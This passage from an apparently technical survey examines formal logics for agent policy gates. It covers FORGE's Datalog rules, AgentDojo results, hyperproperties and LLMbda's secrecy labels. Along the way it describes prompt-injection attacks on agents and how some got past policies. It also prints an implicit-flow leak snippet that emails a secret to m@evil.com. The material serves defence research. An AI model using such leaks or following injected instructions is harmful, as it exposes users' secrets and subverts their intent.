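This counts x as influencing itself through a chain of zero steps, which doesn't affect the rule because a document is not an email. The formula quantifies only over sets of objects, so it belongs to monadic second-order logic, the part of second-order logic with that restriction.

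A second option is to store the transitive closure in the log, as Soteria does. First-order logic can't compute the closure from Flow, but it can check a stored one. Let Influences be the stored relation, and require

$$\forall x\forall y\,\big(\text{Influences}(x,y) \leftrightarrow \text{Flow}(x,y) \vee \exists z\,(\text{Flow}(x,z) \wedge \text{Influences}(z,y))\big).$$

If the log is finite and content flows only from earlier events to later ones, the true closure is the only relation that satisfies this sentence. The sentence determines each event's entries from those of later events, so we can work out every entry by starting at the last event and going backwards. If Flow has loops, other relations can also satisfy the sentence. For example, when the objects are files and two notes copy from each other, a false entry for one note can support a false entry for the other.

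Arithmetic is a third way. With addition and multiplication of natural numbers, a formula can use Gödel's method to encode a whole chain as two numbers. For example, c = 120 and d = 6 encode the chain from event 1 through event 3 to event 6, because dividing 120 by 1 + d = 7, 1 + 2d = 13 and 1 + 3d = 19 leaves the remainders 1, 3 and 6. Some pair c, d encodes any given finite list of natural numbers in this way, so "there is a chain from x to y" becomes "there are numbers c, d and n such that the list encoded by c and d starts at x, reaches y after n steps, and makes a Flow step each time". The formula is first-order because every quantifier ranges over numbers. However, it is hard to read, and no procedure can decide whether each formula of this kind is true.

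### FORGE

*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* uses recursion. Its runtime gate, FORGE, takes policies written in Datalog, a rule language with recursion that an engine evaluates on a finite set of facts. In this language the influence rule takes three lines:

```
Tainted(e) :- UntrustedInput(e).
Tainted(e) :- DependsOn(e, e'), Tainted(e').
Deny(a)    :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a).
```

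The sign `:-` means "if", and a comma means "and". An event is tainted if it is untrusted input or depends on a tainted event. The gate denies an action if the action sends something outside and is tainted. FORGE's version of the last rule also requires the action to carry sensitive data, which a second pair of recursive rules tracks in the same way.

The engine starts from the recorded facts and keeps adding facts that the rules imply until nothing new appears. In the developers' example, an agent reads a vendor's document that contains a planted instruction, reads a confidential file, and tries to email an outside address. The engine first marks the document as tainted, then the events that depend on it, and eventually the email. The process always stops, because a log of n events can produce at most n facts of the form Tainted(e). For a fixed policy, the work grows at most polynomially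 with the number of facts.

FORGE also allows "not" in rules, as in "deny a protected call if it has no approval". The negation is stratified, so the engine finishes computing a relation before any rule uses its negation. This excludes circular rules such as "P holds if P does not hold". With this addition, Datalog can express every first-order rule about a finite set of facts, so policy writers who switch to it can keep every rule from the previous section. The engine treats any fact it cannot derive as false, so it denies a protected call when the approval is missing but may permit a call when a dependency is missing.

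FORGE records dependencies in an event graph, adding an edge from one event to a later one when the later event may have used the earlier one. Several agents can work at the same time, so the graph doesn't put all events in one sequence. It orders events by the same agent or tool, and puts a message before whatever its recipient does after seeing it and a tool call before its result. When a language model writes a message, FORGE records a dependency on every message in the history the model received, because nobody can tell from outside which ones affected what it wrote.

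When an agent proposes an action, FORGE takes these steps:

1. It holds the action and finds the message that led to it.
2. It waits until the Datalog engine has received every event on which that message depends.
3. It gathers facts about the action and its arguments, the verified identity of whoever is acting, and the event graph.
4. It applies the policy. If the rules imply Deny, it blocks the action and returns an explanation to the agent. If they imply Allow and not Deny, it releases the action. If they imply neither, it follows a default setting.

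This takes little time. In a test with 32 agents running at once, the median decision took less than a millisecond, including communication.

An action is guaranteed never to run if the policy implies its denial, as long as every relevant action passes through the gate and the recorded facts are accurate. Agent code that writes directly to a network socket bypasses the gate. If a method starts several tasks in parallel inside itself, the gate may decide on an incomplete graph. Under rules that deny an action because of its history, surplus edges only lead to more blocking, which is why the developers treat them as the safe kind of error. But FORGE also has rules that allow an action because of its history, such as one that lets an agent query a drug database if the query depends on a supervisor's approval. A surplus edge there could let an unapproved query through.

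### What the influence rule costs in practice

The developers tested FORGE on AgentDojo, a benchmark of banking, travel, Slack and office tasks in which some tool outputs contain an attacker's instructions. The agent ran on GPT-4o, a model from 2024. They ran five rounds of 97 ordinary tasks and 949 attacked runs in each setting. Every setting in the results below also repeats the user's request to the model after each batch of tool outputs.

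| Setting | Ordinary tasks completed | Tasks completed under attack | Attacks with an effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| No gate | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% |
| Another model chooses the permitted tools in advance | 73.4% | 69.5% | 3.1% |
| FORGE, information-flow policy | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.3% |
| FORGE, provenance policy | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.2% |

The last column leaves out attacks that AgentDojo counts as successful even though FORGE blocked every call the attacker wanted. With those included, the attack success rates were 0.6% for the information-flow policy and 0.9% for the provenance policy.

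The information-flow policy, taken from an earlier system called FIDES, is close to the influence rule. It blocks every consequential call once the agent's context contains untrusted content, and it also keeps confidential data from recipients who lack clearance. It stops almost every attack, but the agent completes fewer than half as many ordinary tasks as it does without a gate. The chains of influence cause this drop, although the logic handles them correctly. Each message from the model depends on everything the model has seen, so one untrusted document taints all its later actions, including those the user explicitly requested.

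The provenance policy restricts actions based on where each argument came from. A tainted email may go out if the user named the recipient or the operator has listed the recipient. The user must also have asked for the kind of effect the action has, such as a deletion.

Some requests describe their target instead of naming it, such as "delete the largest file". Every identifier in the file listing comes from the same tool output, so an identifier's origin can't show whether the agent chose the right file. FORGE works out the largest file itself and compares it with the agent's choice. At first, the policy accepted a target if any listing in the agent's context selected it. After deleting the largest file, an agent could therefore list the files again and delete the next largest. The policy also accepted the attacker's file if a search result contained only that file. The developers then added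 a rule that denies the deletion if any listing selects a different file.

Under the provenance policy, attacks still succeeded in ten of the 4,745 attacked runs. In all ten, the attacker wanted the agent to recommend a particular hotel in its final answer. That takes no tool call, so FORGE had no action to check. When the prompt did not repeat the user's request, three other attacks got the agent to book an expensive hotel for the dates the user had given. The hotel was in the trusted catalogue, and the policy had no rule about price.

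### Counterexamples that no real system has

A gate evaluates a policy on one finite log. Compactness creates another difficulty for a prover that tries to show that every possible run obeys a rule.

Suppose an assistant has a retry budget that drops by one with each failed call, and it hands the task to a person when the budget reaches zero. If every call fails, the assistant must eventually hand over the task, because the budget starts at some natural number. To prove this in first-order logic, we need axioms for budgets: zero is a budget, every budget has a next one up, different budgets have different next ones, and every budget except zero is one more than another. Now add a constant c and the infinitely many sentences c ≠ 0, c ≠ 1, c ≠ 2 and so on. Any finite number of these sentences are true if c is a large enough natural number. By compactness, some structure satisfies the axioms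 and all of these sentences, and in that structure c cannot be reached by counting up from zero.

Logicians call this a non-standard model. In it, an assistant's budget can start at c and fall to c − 1, c − 2, c − 3 and so on through all the ordinary moments of time without reaching zero. This infinite run satisfies the axioms and contains no handover, so the handover cannot be proved from these axioms. A prover may search forever or report the infinite run as a counterexample. Further first-order axioms cannot remove all such structures, even if they include every first-order sentence that is true of the natural numbers.

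For a particular rule, an induction axiom usually solves the problem. Here the axiom would be that if the statement "from budget n, the assistant eventually reaches zero" holds for n = 0, and holds for n + 1 whenever it holds for n, then it holds for every budget. Adding this axiom rules out the run that starts at c and makes the handover provable. But someone has to find the right statement for each rule.

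Safety properties allow an easier method, because overestimating which states are reachable doesn't invalidate a safety proof. *Simulating reachability using first-order logic* (2009) relies on this for programs that follow links between records in memory. Ordinary first-order provers can't handle transitive closure, and adding it makes even simple decidable parts of first-order logic undecidable. The method therefore replaces closure with first-order axioms that the true closure satisfies but that other relations may satisfy too. A rule that holds for all those relations also holds for the true closure, but a violation found by the prover may be spurious.

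Lisitsa (2010), in *Finite Model Finding for Parameterized Verification*, uses the search for counterexamples to prove safety. The axioms state that the starting state is reachable and that any step from a reachable state leads to a reachable state. If the system could reach a bad state, applying these axioms a finite number of times would prove it. The system is therefore safe if there is a single structure in which the axioms hold and the bad state is not reachable.

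Such a structure can be tiny even if the system has infinitely many states. Take a counter that starts at 0 and goes up by 2 at each step. A structure with two objects, one for all even numbers and one for all odd numbers, is enough to show that the counter never reaches 5. Adding 1 leads from either object to the other, so adding 2 leads back to the same object. Since the counter starts at 0, only the even object is reachable, and 5 is odd. Lisitsa uses general-purpose programs to search for these structures. He proves that the method solves every safety problem that can be solved by regular model checking, an established technique that uses finite automata to represent infinite sets of states.

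### Lindström's theorem

Since compactness causes so much trouble, one might want a logic that can express chains and keeps the useful features of first-order logic. Per Lindström proved in 1969 how far that is possible. His theorem concerns any logic that can express everything first-order logic can and that meets some basic conditions, for instance that it has "and", "not" and "there is". Suppose the logic also has two properties:

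- If every finite part of a countable set of its sentences is true in some structure, then some structure makes the whole set true (countable compactness).
- If a sentence is true in some structure, it is true in one with at most countably many objects (the downward Löwenheim–Skolem property).

Then every sentence of the logic is equivalent to a first-order sentence. A logic that can express more must lack at least one of the two properties.

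First-order logic with a transitive closure operator is not compact. In that logic, I(d, e) means that a finite chain exists, so every finite part of the set used above can be satisfied, but the whole set cannot. The logic still has the Löwenheim–Skolem property, but it cannot have a complete proof system. Transitive closure can express that every number is reachable from 0 by adding one finitely many times, which rules out non-standard numbers. A complete proof system could then be used to list all the truths of arithmetic, and Gödel's work showed that no procedure can do this. Full second-order logic has neither of Lindström's two properties. First-order logic with the added quantifier "there are uncountably many" is countably compact but lacks the Löwenheim–Skolem property.

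These losses matter for proving things about all possible runs and for analysing a policy before anyone uses it. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* suggests checking policies for contradictions and redundant rules, but warns that such checks are not always complete for recursive policies. The losses do not affect FORGE's decisions, which concern one finite set of facts at a time.

### Every second step

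The audit rule concerns only the even steps, and the game showed that first-order logic with only order cannot distinguish odd steps from even ones. By Kamp's theorem, LTL cannot either. *Temporal Logic Can Be More Expressive* (Wolper, 1983) proves this directly and shows where LTL fails.

LTL can express the requirement that steps without and with an audit alternate, starting with a step without one. This requirement cannot replace the audit rule because it is stricter. An assistant that logs an audit at every step obeys the audit rule but violates the alternation requirement.

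Wolper considers runs that, in our terms, have exactly one missing audit, at step i + 1. The assistant obeys the rule if i + 1 is odd and breaks it if i + 1 is even. Wolper proves that an LTL formula with n "next" operators has the same truth value in all such runs with i greater than n. The formula therefore has the same truth value for i = n + 1 and i = n + 2, although the assistant breaks the rule in exactly one of those runs.

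The proof is by induction on the structure of the formula. Each "next" moves the point of evaluation one step forward, leaving one fewer audit before the gap, and there are more than n audits to begin with. "Always" and "until" can reach arbitrarily far ahead, but they evaluate their parts on the remainder of the run, which is again a run with a gap and fewer audits before it. By the induction hypothesis, those parts have the same truth value on all remainders with more than n audits before the gap, and remainders with n or fewer occur in every run being compared. The same argument applies to any rule about every m-th step, where m is at least 2.

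Monadic second-order logic can state the audit rule by asking for a set E that marks the even steps:

$$\exists E\,\big[\forall x\,(\text{First}(x) \rightarrow \neg E(x)) \wedge \forall x\forall y\,(\text{Next}(x,y) \rightarrow (E(y) \leftrightarrow \neg E(x))) \wedge \forall x\,(E(x) \rightarrow \text{Audit}(x))\big].$$

First and Next are abbreviations that can be defined using <. In any run, only the set of steps at even positions satisfies the first two conditions, and the last condition requires an audit at each of those steps. This is the earlier formula with the symbol Even, except that it now defines the set itself instead of relying on the class of structures to supply it.

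A monitor for the rule is trivial to build, because it needs only an automaton with three states: the next step is odd, the next step is even, and the rule has been broken. If the events have finitely many types, monadic second-order logic can define exactly those properties of finite runs that a finite automaton can recognise.

Cohen, Perrin and Pin (1993), in *On the Expressive Power of Temporal Logic*, prove an algebraic criterion for when LTL can express a rule. It amounts to a test on the smallest automaton for the rule. LTL can express the rule exactly when no sequence of events, if repeated, can make the automaton cycle forever through two or more states. The audit automaton fails because repeated audits switch it back and forth between odd and even. The automaton for "look up before cancelling" passes because it stays in the same state after one lookup. A program can run this test,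 so a policy writer who has an automaton can find out whether an LTL formula exists.

Extensions of LTL differ in how much computation they require. Deciding whether any run satisfies an LTL formula is PSPACE-complete, so the memory required grows at most polynomially with the length of the formula. Adding quantifiers over sets of steps keeps the problem decidable, but no fixed tower of exponentials bounds the time or memory required. Wolper proposes a less demanding extension, in which users define new temporal operators with simple grammars. One such operator has the pattern "anything, then an audit, then repeat". The extended logic can express the audit rule, and its decision problem is still PSPACE-complete.

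### Running totals

The spending rule caps the total amount transferred to each recipient each day. A first-order formula that can use addition can limit the sum of any two transfers, or of any three, but a recipient may receive any number of transfers in a day. Chains can also be any length, but here the cap can limit how many transfers the formula must check at once. Suppose every amount is a whole number of at least 1 and the cap is 500. If a day's total exceeds 500, then some group of at most 501 transfers already adds up to more than 500. A first-order sentence can therefore state the rule exactly by limiting the sum of every group of up to 501 transfers to the same recipient on the same day. That sentence would be too long to be practical, and with amounts in cents the groups would grow to 50,001. If the cap differs from customer to customer with no fixed maximum, this method fails,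 and the language needs a way to add up arbitrarily many amounts.

The rule is simple to implement in a program that keeps one counter for each recipient and day. Before each transfer, the program checks whether the total so far plus the new amount stays within the cap. Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, studies policies of this kind for tool-using agents and uses the spending rule as an example. His policies are automata with counters, including a separate counter for each value of a key such as the recipient. Adding the date to the key starts a new counter each day, so no counter has to be reset. A trusted clock must supply the date, because an agent that could choose its own dates could avoid the cap. FORGE's Datalog has no built-in notion of time, so rate limits in it need hand-written rules about timestamps.

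Ray asks what a program can find out about such a policy before anyone uses it. The most basic check is whether the policy can ever block anything, since a policy that no run could violate probably contains a mistake. He proves that no procedure can perform this check for every policy if policies may use two counters that can be increased, decreased and tested for zero.

The proof starts from programs with two counters. Each instruction either adds one to a counter, or checks whether a counter is zero and subtracts one if it is not. Such programs can carry out any computation, so no procedure can decide for every one whether it halts. Ray turns each program into a policy that runs one instruction every time the agent takes an action called "tick" and forbids the tick that would make the program halt. Some run violates the policy if and only if the program halts. Enforcing the policy is still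 easy, because a gate only has to run one instruction per tick.

He also defines a restricted class of policies for which the check is decidable and needs only polynomial memory. Counters in this class only go up. Each test compares one counter, or one counter plus the amount in the proposed action, with a fixed number. An action that names a recipient can read and change only that recipient's counters. The spending rule meets these conditions, as do the rules "authenticate before access" and "send nothing after the user revokes permission".

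Two facts make the check possible. First, the check can treat all totals above the cap as one value, which leaves finitely many cases. If the cap is 500, totals of 501 and 50,000 have the same consequences, because a total that only goes up never returns to 500 or less. Second, the check only needs to track one recipient, however many the agent pays. If a run breaks the cap for Ana, the same run with everyone else's transfers removed also breaks it, because those transfers don't affect her total.

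The gate itself still has to store a total for every recipient, but the time it takes to find the right total grows only with the logarithm of the number of recipients. Ray supports his proof with a program that compares the simplified and exact counters in every case for caps up to three and runs of up to five actions. He describes this as a check for errors, not a machine-checked proof.

Small changes to a policy can take it outside the restricted class. The counter has to go down if refunds lower a recipient's total, or if a cap applies to every 24-hour period instead of every calendar day, since old transfers must then be subtracted. The calendar-day cap is weaker because it allows 500 just before midnight and another 500 just after. Even counters that only go up become too powerful if a policy can compare them with each other. If one counter records additions and another records subtractions,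 the two are equal exactly when the balance is zero, so together they can simulate a counter that goes up and down. A rule such as "never send more to new recipients than to existing ones" requires this kind of comparison.

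## Secrecy, robustness and risk: requirements on many runs at once

A gate can check every rule in the previous two sections from the log of a single run. The secrecy rule, however, forbids outputs that depend on a secret, and no language can express that as a property of single runs. Two very small systems are enough to prove this.

### Two systems that no single-run property can separate

In both systems, the assistant knows one secret bit, for example whether a customer has a poor credit record, and then outputs one public bit. We write each run as a pair (secret, output).

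- The Copier shows the secret. Its possible runs are (0,0) and (1,1).
- The Flipper tosses a fair coin and shows the result. Its possible runs are (0,0), (0,1), (1,0) and (1,1).

Suppose some property of single runs captured the secrecy rule, so that a system keeps its secret exactly when all its runs have the property. The Flipper reveals nothing, so all four of its runs have the property. Both of the Copier's runs are among those four, so the Copier passes too, even though it leaks the secret. Therefore no property of single runs can capture the secrecy rule.

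The argument also works without the coin. A system that always shows 0 and a system that always shows 1 are both secure, and together they have the same four runs. So a single-run property that accepts both also accepts the Copier.

Michael Clarkson and Fred Schneider introduced the term "hyperproperty" in 2008 for requirements of this kind. A property of single runs is a set of runs, but a hyperproperty is a set of sets of runs, because it applies to a system's whole set of runs. The Flipper's set of four runs satisfies the secrecy rule, but the Copier's set of two does not.

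### HyperLTL

The most widely used language for hyperproperties extends LTL. Finkbeiner (2025), in *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties*, surveys this language, HyperLTL, and its relatives. A HyperLTL formula begins with quantifiers over runs, followed by an LTL formula in which every proposition carries the name of a run:

$$\varphi ::= \forall\pi.\,\varphi \mid \exists\pi.\,\varphi \mid \psi \qquad\qquad \psi ::= a_\pi \mid \neg\psi \mid \psi\wedge\psi \mid \mathsf{X}\,\psi \mid \psi\,\mathsf{U}\,\psi$$

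Here $a_\pi$ means that proposition a holds at the current step of run π. The quantifiers range over the runs of the system being examined. The temporal operators move along all the chosen runs together, so $\mathsf{G}(o_\pi \leftrightarrow o_{\pi'})$ means that the outputs of π and π′ agree at every step.

Let h be a secret input, l a public input and o an output. One version of the secrecy rule, called observational determinism, is

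$$\forall\pi\,\forall\pi'.\;(l_\pi \leftrightarrow l_{\pi'}) \rightarrow \mathsf{G}(o_\pi \leftrightarrow o_{\pi'}).$$

Observational determinism requires any two runs that start with the same public input to have the same outputs. This correctly rules out the Copier, but it also rules out the Flipper, whose runs (0,0) and (0,1) have the same public input and different outputs. The requirement is too strict for any system that chooses its outputs at random, as language models usually do.

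Generalised noninterference allows random choice:

$$\forall\pi\,\forall\pi'\,\exists\pi''.\;\mathsf{G}\big((h_\pi \leftrightarrow h_{\pi''}) \wedge (l_{\pi'} \leftrightarrow l_{\pi''}) \wedge (o_{\pi'} \leftrightarrow o_{\pi''})\big).$$

For any two runs, the system must also have a run that combines the secret from the first with the public inputs and outputs from the second. An observer who sees only the public part of a run then cannot rule out any secret that the system might hold.

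We can check this formula on the Flipper, whose public input is the same in every run. Four runs give sixteen choices of π and π′, but only two values of the secret and two of the output matter.

| Secret in π | Output in π′ | Run needed as π″ | In the Flipper? |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 | (0,0) | Yes |
| 0 | 1 | (0,1) | Yes |
| 1 | 0 | (1,0) | Yes |
| 1 | 1 | (1,1) | Yes |

The formula is true. If we remove the run (0,1), it becomes false, because the second row no longer has a π″. This is the correct result, since an observer who sees output 1 can now conclude that the secret is 1.

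*Verifying Hyperliveness* (Coenen, Finkbeiner and colleagues, 2020) uses definitions that extend safety and liveness to sets of runs. If a system violates a hypersafety property, finitely many finite logs are enough to show the violation, whatever other runs the system has. Observational determinism is a hypersafety property, because two logs with equal public inputs and different outputs refute it. For a hyperliveness property, any finite collection of finite logs can be extended to a set of runs that satisfies it. Generalised noninterference is a hyperliveness property, so an auditor cannot refute it from any collection of logs. A run whose absence seems to violate it may be one that the system can produce but has not yet produced. As with Alpern and Schneider's result for single runs, every hyperproperty is the intersection of a hypersafety property and a hyperliveness property.

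Even observational determinism takes more work to monitor than the rules in earlier sections. A monitor has to keep the logs of past sessions and compare each new session with all of them, so the thousandth session requires 999 comparisons. When several logs begin the same way, storing that beginning only once reduces the work.

Generalised noninterference also has a gap, because it concerns only which runs are possible. Suppose the Flipper's coin is biased so that the output equals the secret 99% of the time. The same four runs are still possible, so the formula is still true, but anyone who sees the output can guess the secret almost perfectly. Ruling this out requires probabilities, which HyperLTL does not have.

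### Robustness

Robustness means that similar inputs lead to similar outputs. It compares two runs, so HyperLTL can express it in the same form as secrecy. Let d measure the distance between two inputs or two outputs, and choose limits $\kappa_i$ and $\kappa_o$. For a system without random choice, one can write

$$\forall\pi\,\forall\pi'.\;\big(d(o_\pi,o_{\pi'}) \le \kappa_o\big)\;\mathsf{W}\;\big(d(i_\pi,i_{\pi'}) > \kappa_i\big).$$

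The operator W ("weak until") means that the left side holds at every step before the right side first becomes true, or forever if it never does. If two customers send nearly the same complaint, their refunds must stay within $\kappa_o$ of each other until their messages differ by more than $\kappa_i$.

Coenen and colleagues give a version for systems with random choice, known as robust cleanness:

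$$\forall\pi\,\forall\pi'\,\exists\pi''.\;\mathsf{G}(i_{\pi'} = i_{\pi''}) \wedge \Big(\big(d(o_\pi,o_{\pi''}) \le \kappa_o\big)\;\mathsf{W}\;\big(d(i_\pi,i_{\pi''}) > \kappa_i\big)\Big).$$

The system must have at least one run that responds to the inputs of π′ with outputs close to those of π, but not every run on those inputs has to do so. The formula can be used to detect software doping, in which a manufacturer gives a product hidden behaviour that appears only in special circumstances, such as an official test.

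Whoever writes the requirement has to choose the distance measure d. For a sensor reading, d can be the difference between two numbers. For text, the choice is much harder. "Cancel the booking" and "Do not cancel the booking" are close if d counts changed words, but a robust assistant should treat them very differently.

### First-order logic over sets of runs

First-order logic can also express these requirements if the structure contains many runs. Finkbeiner and Zimmermann (2016), in *The First-Order Logic of Hyperproperties*, take as objects all pairs of a run and a time step. The formula x < y means that x and y lie on the same run and x comes first. A new symbol E, the equal-level predicate, relates two objects with the same time step, whichever runs they lie on. With Min(x) as an abbreviation for "x is the first step of its run", observational determinism becomes

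$$\forall x\forall y\,\Big(\text{Min}(x)\wedge\text{Min}(y)\wedge(L(x)\leftrightarrow L(y)) \rightarrow \forall u\forall v\,\big(x\le u\wedge y\le v\wedge E(u,v)\rightarrow(O(u)\leftrightarrow O(v))\big)\Big).$$

Every quantifier ranges over objects, so the formula is first-order. Without E, a formula could not match step 5 of one run with step 5 of another.

For single runs, Kamp's theorem makes first-order logic and LTL equally expressive. For sets of runs the two separate. Finkbeiner and Zimmermann show that a first-order formula can replace every HyperLTL formula, but not the other way round. Suppose an operator wants to fix in advance a moment for installing an update, and the assistant must be idle at that moment however the session has gone. The first-order formula is

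$$\exists x\,\forall y\,(E(x,y)\rightarrow\text{Idle}(y)).$$

The HyperLTL formula $\forall\pi.\,\mathsf{F}\,\text{Idle}_\pi$ means that every run is idle at some time. The idle moment may differ from run to run, because the time is chosen after the run. Laura Bozzelli and colleagues proved in 2015 that no HyperLTL formula can require all runs to be idle at the same moment. A HyperLTL formula can compare only as many runs at once as it has run variables, but a common idle moment involves every run, and there may be infinitely many.

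Finkbeiner describes this formula as setting a common deadline for all runs, but it is stricter than an ordinary deadline. HyperLTL can express the rule "there is a time limit within which every run gets an answer", because it can refer to the slowest run:

$$\exists\pi\,\forall\pi'.\;\mathsf{F}\,\text{Answer}_\pi \wedge (\neg\text{Answer}_\pi\;\mathsf{U}\;\text{Answer}_{\pi'}).$$

If a common limit exists, some run is the last to get its first answer, and that run can serve as π. Conversely, the time of the first answer in π is a limit for every other run. This method fails for the idle moment because an assistant can become idle and then busy again, so there is no slowest run to use as π.

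Finkbeiner and Zimmermann also identify the part of first-order logic that matches HyperLTL exactly. In this fragment, a formula first picks the starting points of some runs, and every later quantifier ranges only over objects on one of those runs. To translate such a formula into HyperLTL, they merge the chosen runs into a single run, each step of which records what happens at that step in all of them. Two objects at equal levels then become the same step, so E becomes "=", and Kamp's theorem applies to the merged run.

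Stronger logics add quantifiers over sets. In the table, a "yes" in the last column means that some procedure can decide, for every formula of the logic and every finite-state system, whether the system satisfies the formula.

| Logic | Quantifiers range over | Example of what it adds | Decidable for finite-state systems? |
|---|---|---|---|
| HyperLTL | Runs | Generalised noninterference | Yes |
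| First-order logic with E | Single steps of any run | A common idle moment | Yes |
| HyperQPTL | Runs, and sets of time steps | All runs agree on a proposition at every even step | Yes |
| Monadic second-order logic with E | Steps, and sets of steps on any runs | A given Turing machine halts | No |

Each logic in the table is strictly more expressive than the one above it. But the single-run counterparts of the first two are equally expressive, and so are those of the last two. HyperQPTL can also express what an agent knows. An agent knows a fact at some moment if the fact holds in every run that has looked the same to the agent so far.

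Another family of logics can also quantify over the ways a run might continue from its current state. *Model Checking Algorithms for Hyperproperties* (Finkbeiner, 2021) gives a decision procedure for one such logic, which allows second-order quantifiers only over complete paths. The problem becomes undecidable if the quantifiers can range over arbitrary sets.

### The cost of checking

Model checking tests whether a finite-state system satisfies a formula. For formulas that use only "for all runs", such as observational determinism, the usual method is to run two copies of the system side by side and check an ordinary LTL formula on the pair. A system with 1,000 states gives at most a million pairs of states, which is manageable.

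A formula becomes harder to check each time it switches between "for all" and "there is". To check a formula of the form $\forall\pi\,\exists\pi'$, the basic algorithm builds an automaton that accepts each run π for which a suitable π′ exists. To find out whether the system has a run that this automaton rejects, it then builds the automaton's complement, which can be exponentially larger. Each further switch can require another complement, and so another exponential increase in size. Generalised noninterference has one switch, and checking it takes memory polynomial in the size of the system but exponential in the length of the formula.

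Coenen and colleagues avoid the complement by treating the check as a game in which one player builds π state by state and the other builds π′ alongside it. If the second player has a strategy that always produces a suitable π′, the formula is true. The method can miss true formulas, because the second player's right choice may depend on what π does later. Adding variables that reveal the necessary facts about the future can solve this.

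A policy writer may also want to know whether any set of runs could satisfy a list of requirements, before a system exists. This is the satisfiability problem. It is decidable for formulas in which every "there is" comes before every "for all", but undecidable once a "there is" may depend on a "for all". Finkbeiner and Zimmermann show how quickly such formulas become complicated. Take these three conditions:

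- Proposition a holds exactly once on every run.
- Some run has a at its first step.
- For every run, some run has a exactly one step later.

Only an infinite set of runs satisfies all three conditions, with one run having *a* at step 1, another at step 2, and so on. In contrast, if any run satisfies an LTL formula, so does a run that eventually repeats itself. Using similar conditions, Finkbeiner and Zimmermann write a HyperLTL formula that marks exactly the prime numbers.

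### FOLHyper

A program can still settle many individual cases of an undecidable problem. *Checking Satisfiability of Hyperproperties using First-Order Logic* (Beutner and Finkbeiner, 2025) presents FOLHyper, a tool that translates HyperLTL into ordinary first-order logic and passes the result to existing provers. The tool can show that two requirements contradict each other. It can also show that requirement A implies requirement B, by showing that "A and not B" is contradictory.

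The translation uses two kinds of object, runs and times, with a constant for the first time and a function that gives the next one. If the part of the formula after the run quantifiers is a safety property, an automaton with "bad" states can recognise its violations. FOLHyper adds a predicate for each state of this automaton, which holds at a given time if the automaton can be in that state when it reads the chosen runs. First-order clauses require that the automaton starts correctly, each step matches what happens in the runs, and it never enters a bad state.

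First-order clauses cannot exclude non-standard times, for the same reason that they could not exclude the retry budget that never reached zero. The extra times do no harm here, because we can turn a structure found by a prover into real runs by starting at the first time and repeatedly moving to the next. The clauses hold at every time we reach, and we can ignore the rest. This argument fails for liveness properties, because the promised event might happen only at a non-standard time. FOLHyper then has to add integer arithmetic, and current solvers often fail on the resulting formulas.

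Beutner and Finkbeiner compared generalised noninterference with noninference, a related rule which requires that for every run there is another with the same public inputs and outputs in which the secret input is always off. For versions of the rules limited to a few steps, FOLHyper showed that neither implies the other. When they also assumed that the system has at least one run with the secret input always off, FOLHyper proved in 0.23 seconds that generalised noninterference implies noninference.

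FOLHyper also detects requirements that no system can meet together. Suppose one clause of a specification requires generalised noninterference and another requires the output to equal the secret input at every step. A system can satisfy both if its secret input is the same in every run. When Beutner and Finkbeiner added a requirement that two runs have different secret inputs, FOLHyper proved the requirements contradictory in 0.25 seconds. They say no earlier tool could prove a contradiction for formulas with arbitrary quantifiers over runs.

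FOLHyper is also fast on some formulas that other tools can decide. One test used rules of the form "an input can lead to at most n different outputs". To decide whether the rule for n = 5 implies the rule for n = 4, an earlier tool, EAHyper, took 15 seconds and FOLHyper took 0.18 seconds. When the test was whether the rule for n = 6 implies the rule for n = 4, EAHyper ran out of time after a minute and FOLHyper took 0.19 seconds.

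Every prover that Beutner and Finkbeiner tried failed on formulas that only infinite sets of runs satisfy, such as one built from the three conditions above. This agrees with the theory. Given enough time, a first-order prover can show that any contradictory formula is contradictory, as long as the translation needs no arithmetic, but no procedure can confirm satisfiability for every satisfiable formula. The results also concern only the requirements, so the consistency of a specification is no evidence that a particular agent meets it.

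### Secrecy for agent programs: LLMbda

Model checking needs a finite-state description of the system, which nobody has for a language model that writes and runs code. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) instead defines a small programming language for agents, LLMbda, and proves that every program in it obeys a secrecy rule.

Every value in LLMbda has a label that can mark it as secret, untrusted or both. Anything computed from a secret value is also secret. The agent's conversation with the model has its own label, because a reply may depend on everything in the conversation. A program can open a temporary copy of the conversation, clear the copy, put tainted material into it and then discard it, so that the main conversation stays clean.

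Labels are easy to get wrong when a secret affects what a program does not do. Garby and colleagues describe a leak of this sort in CaMeL, an earlier defence that also runs model-written code under label checks. The trick, which goes back to Fenton, looks roughly like this:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
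```

If the balance is above the threshold, the third line sets tmp to False and marks it as secret. The program then skips the assignment in the fourth line, so rich keeps its value and its public label, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, no email goes out. The email therefore reveals the secret, although the system detected no secret value reaching it.

In LLMbda, the conversation is the part of a program's state that such a trick could exploit. The interpreter stops any program that would add a message to a conversation not yet marked as secret while inside a branch chosen by a secret. This rule applies to single runs and is stricter than secrecy requires, because it also stops a program that sends the same message in both branches, which would reveal nothing. A gate that checks one run at a time can enforce a hyperproperty only by blocking some harmless behaviour too. Even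 a verifier with access to the whole program would have to reject some harmless programs, since no procedure can certify secrecy for arbitrary programs.

Because the model's replies are random, the theorem compares probability distributions. Take two starting situations that look the same to an observer who can't see secrets. The ideal requirement would be that the observer sees each result with the same probability in both. LLMbda cannot guarantee this, because a program may get stuck or run forever in one situation and not in the other. The theorem allows for such differences. Suppose a program gives these results:

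| | "yes" | "no" | No result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Secret is 0 | 0.5 | 0.3 | 0.2 |
| Secret is 1 | 0.4 | 0.5 | 0.1 |

Garby and colleagues call two distributions compatible if some third distribution gives each result at least as much probability as either of them does, without exceeding a total of 1. Here "yes" needs 0.5 and "no" needs 0.5, which total 1, so the two rows are compatible. The program could be behaving identically in both situations, except that it fails to finish in different cases. If the second row were 0.2, 0.7 and 0.1, the third distribution would need 0.5 + 0.7 = 1.2, which exceeds 1. The biased coin fails this test because it always gives a result, and compatible distributions that always give a result must be equal.

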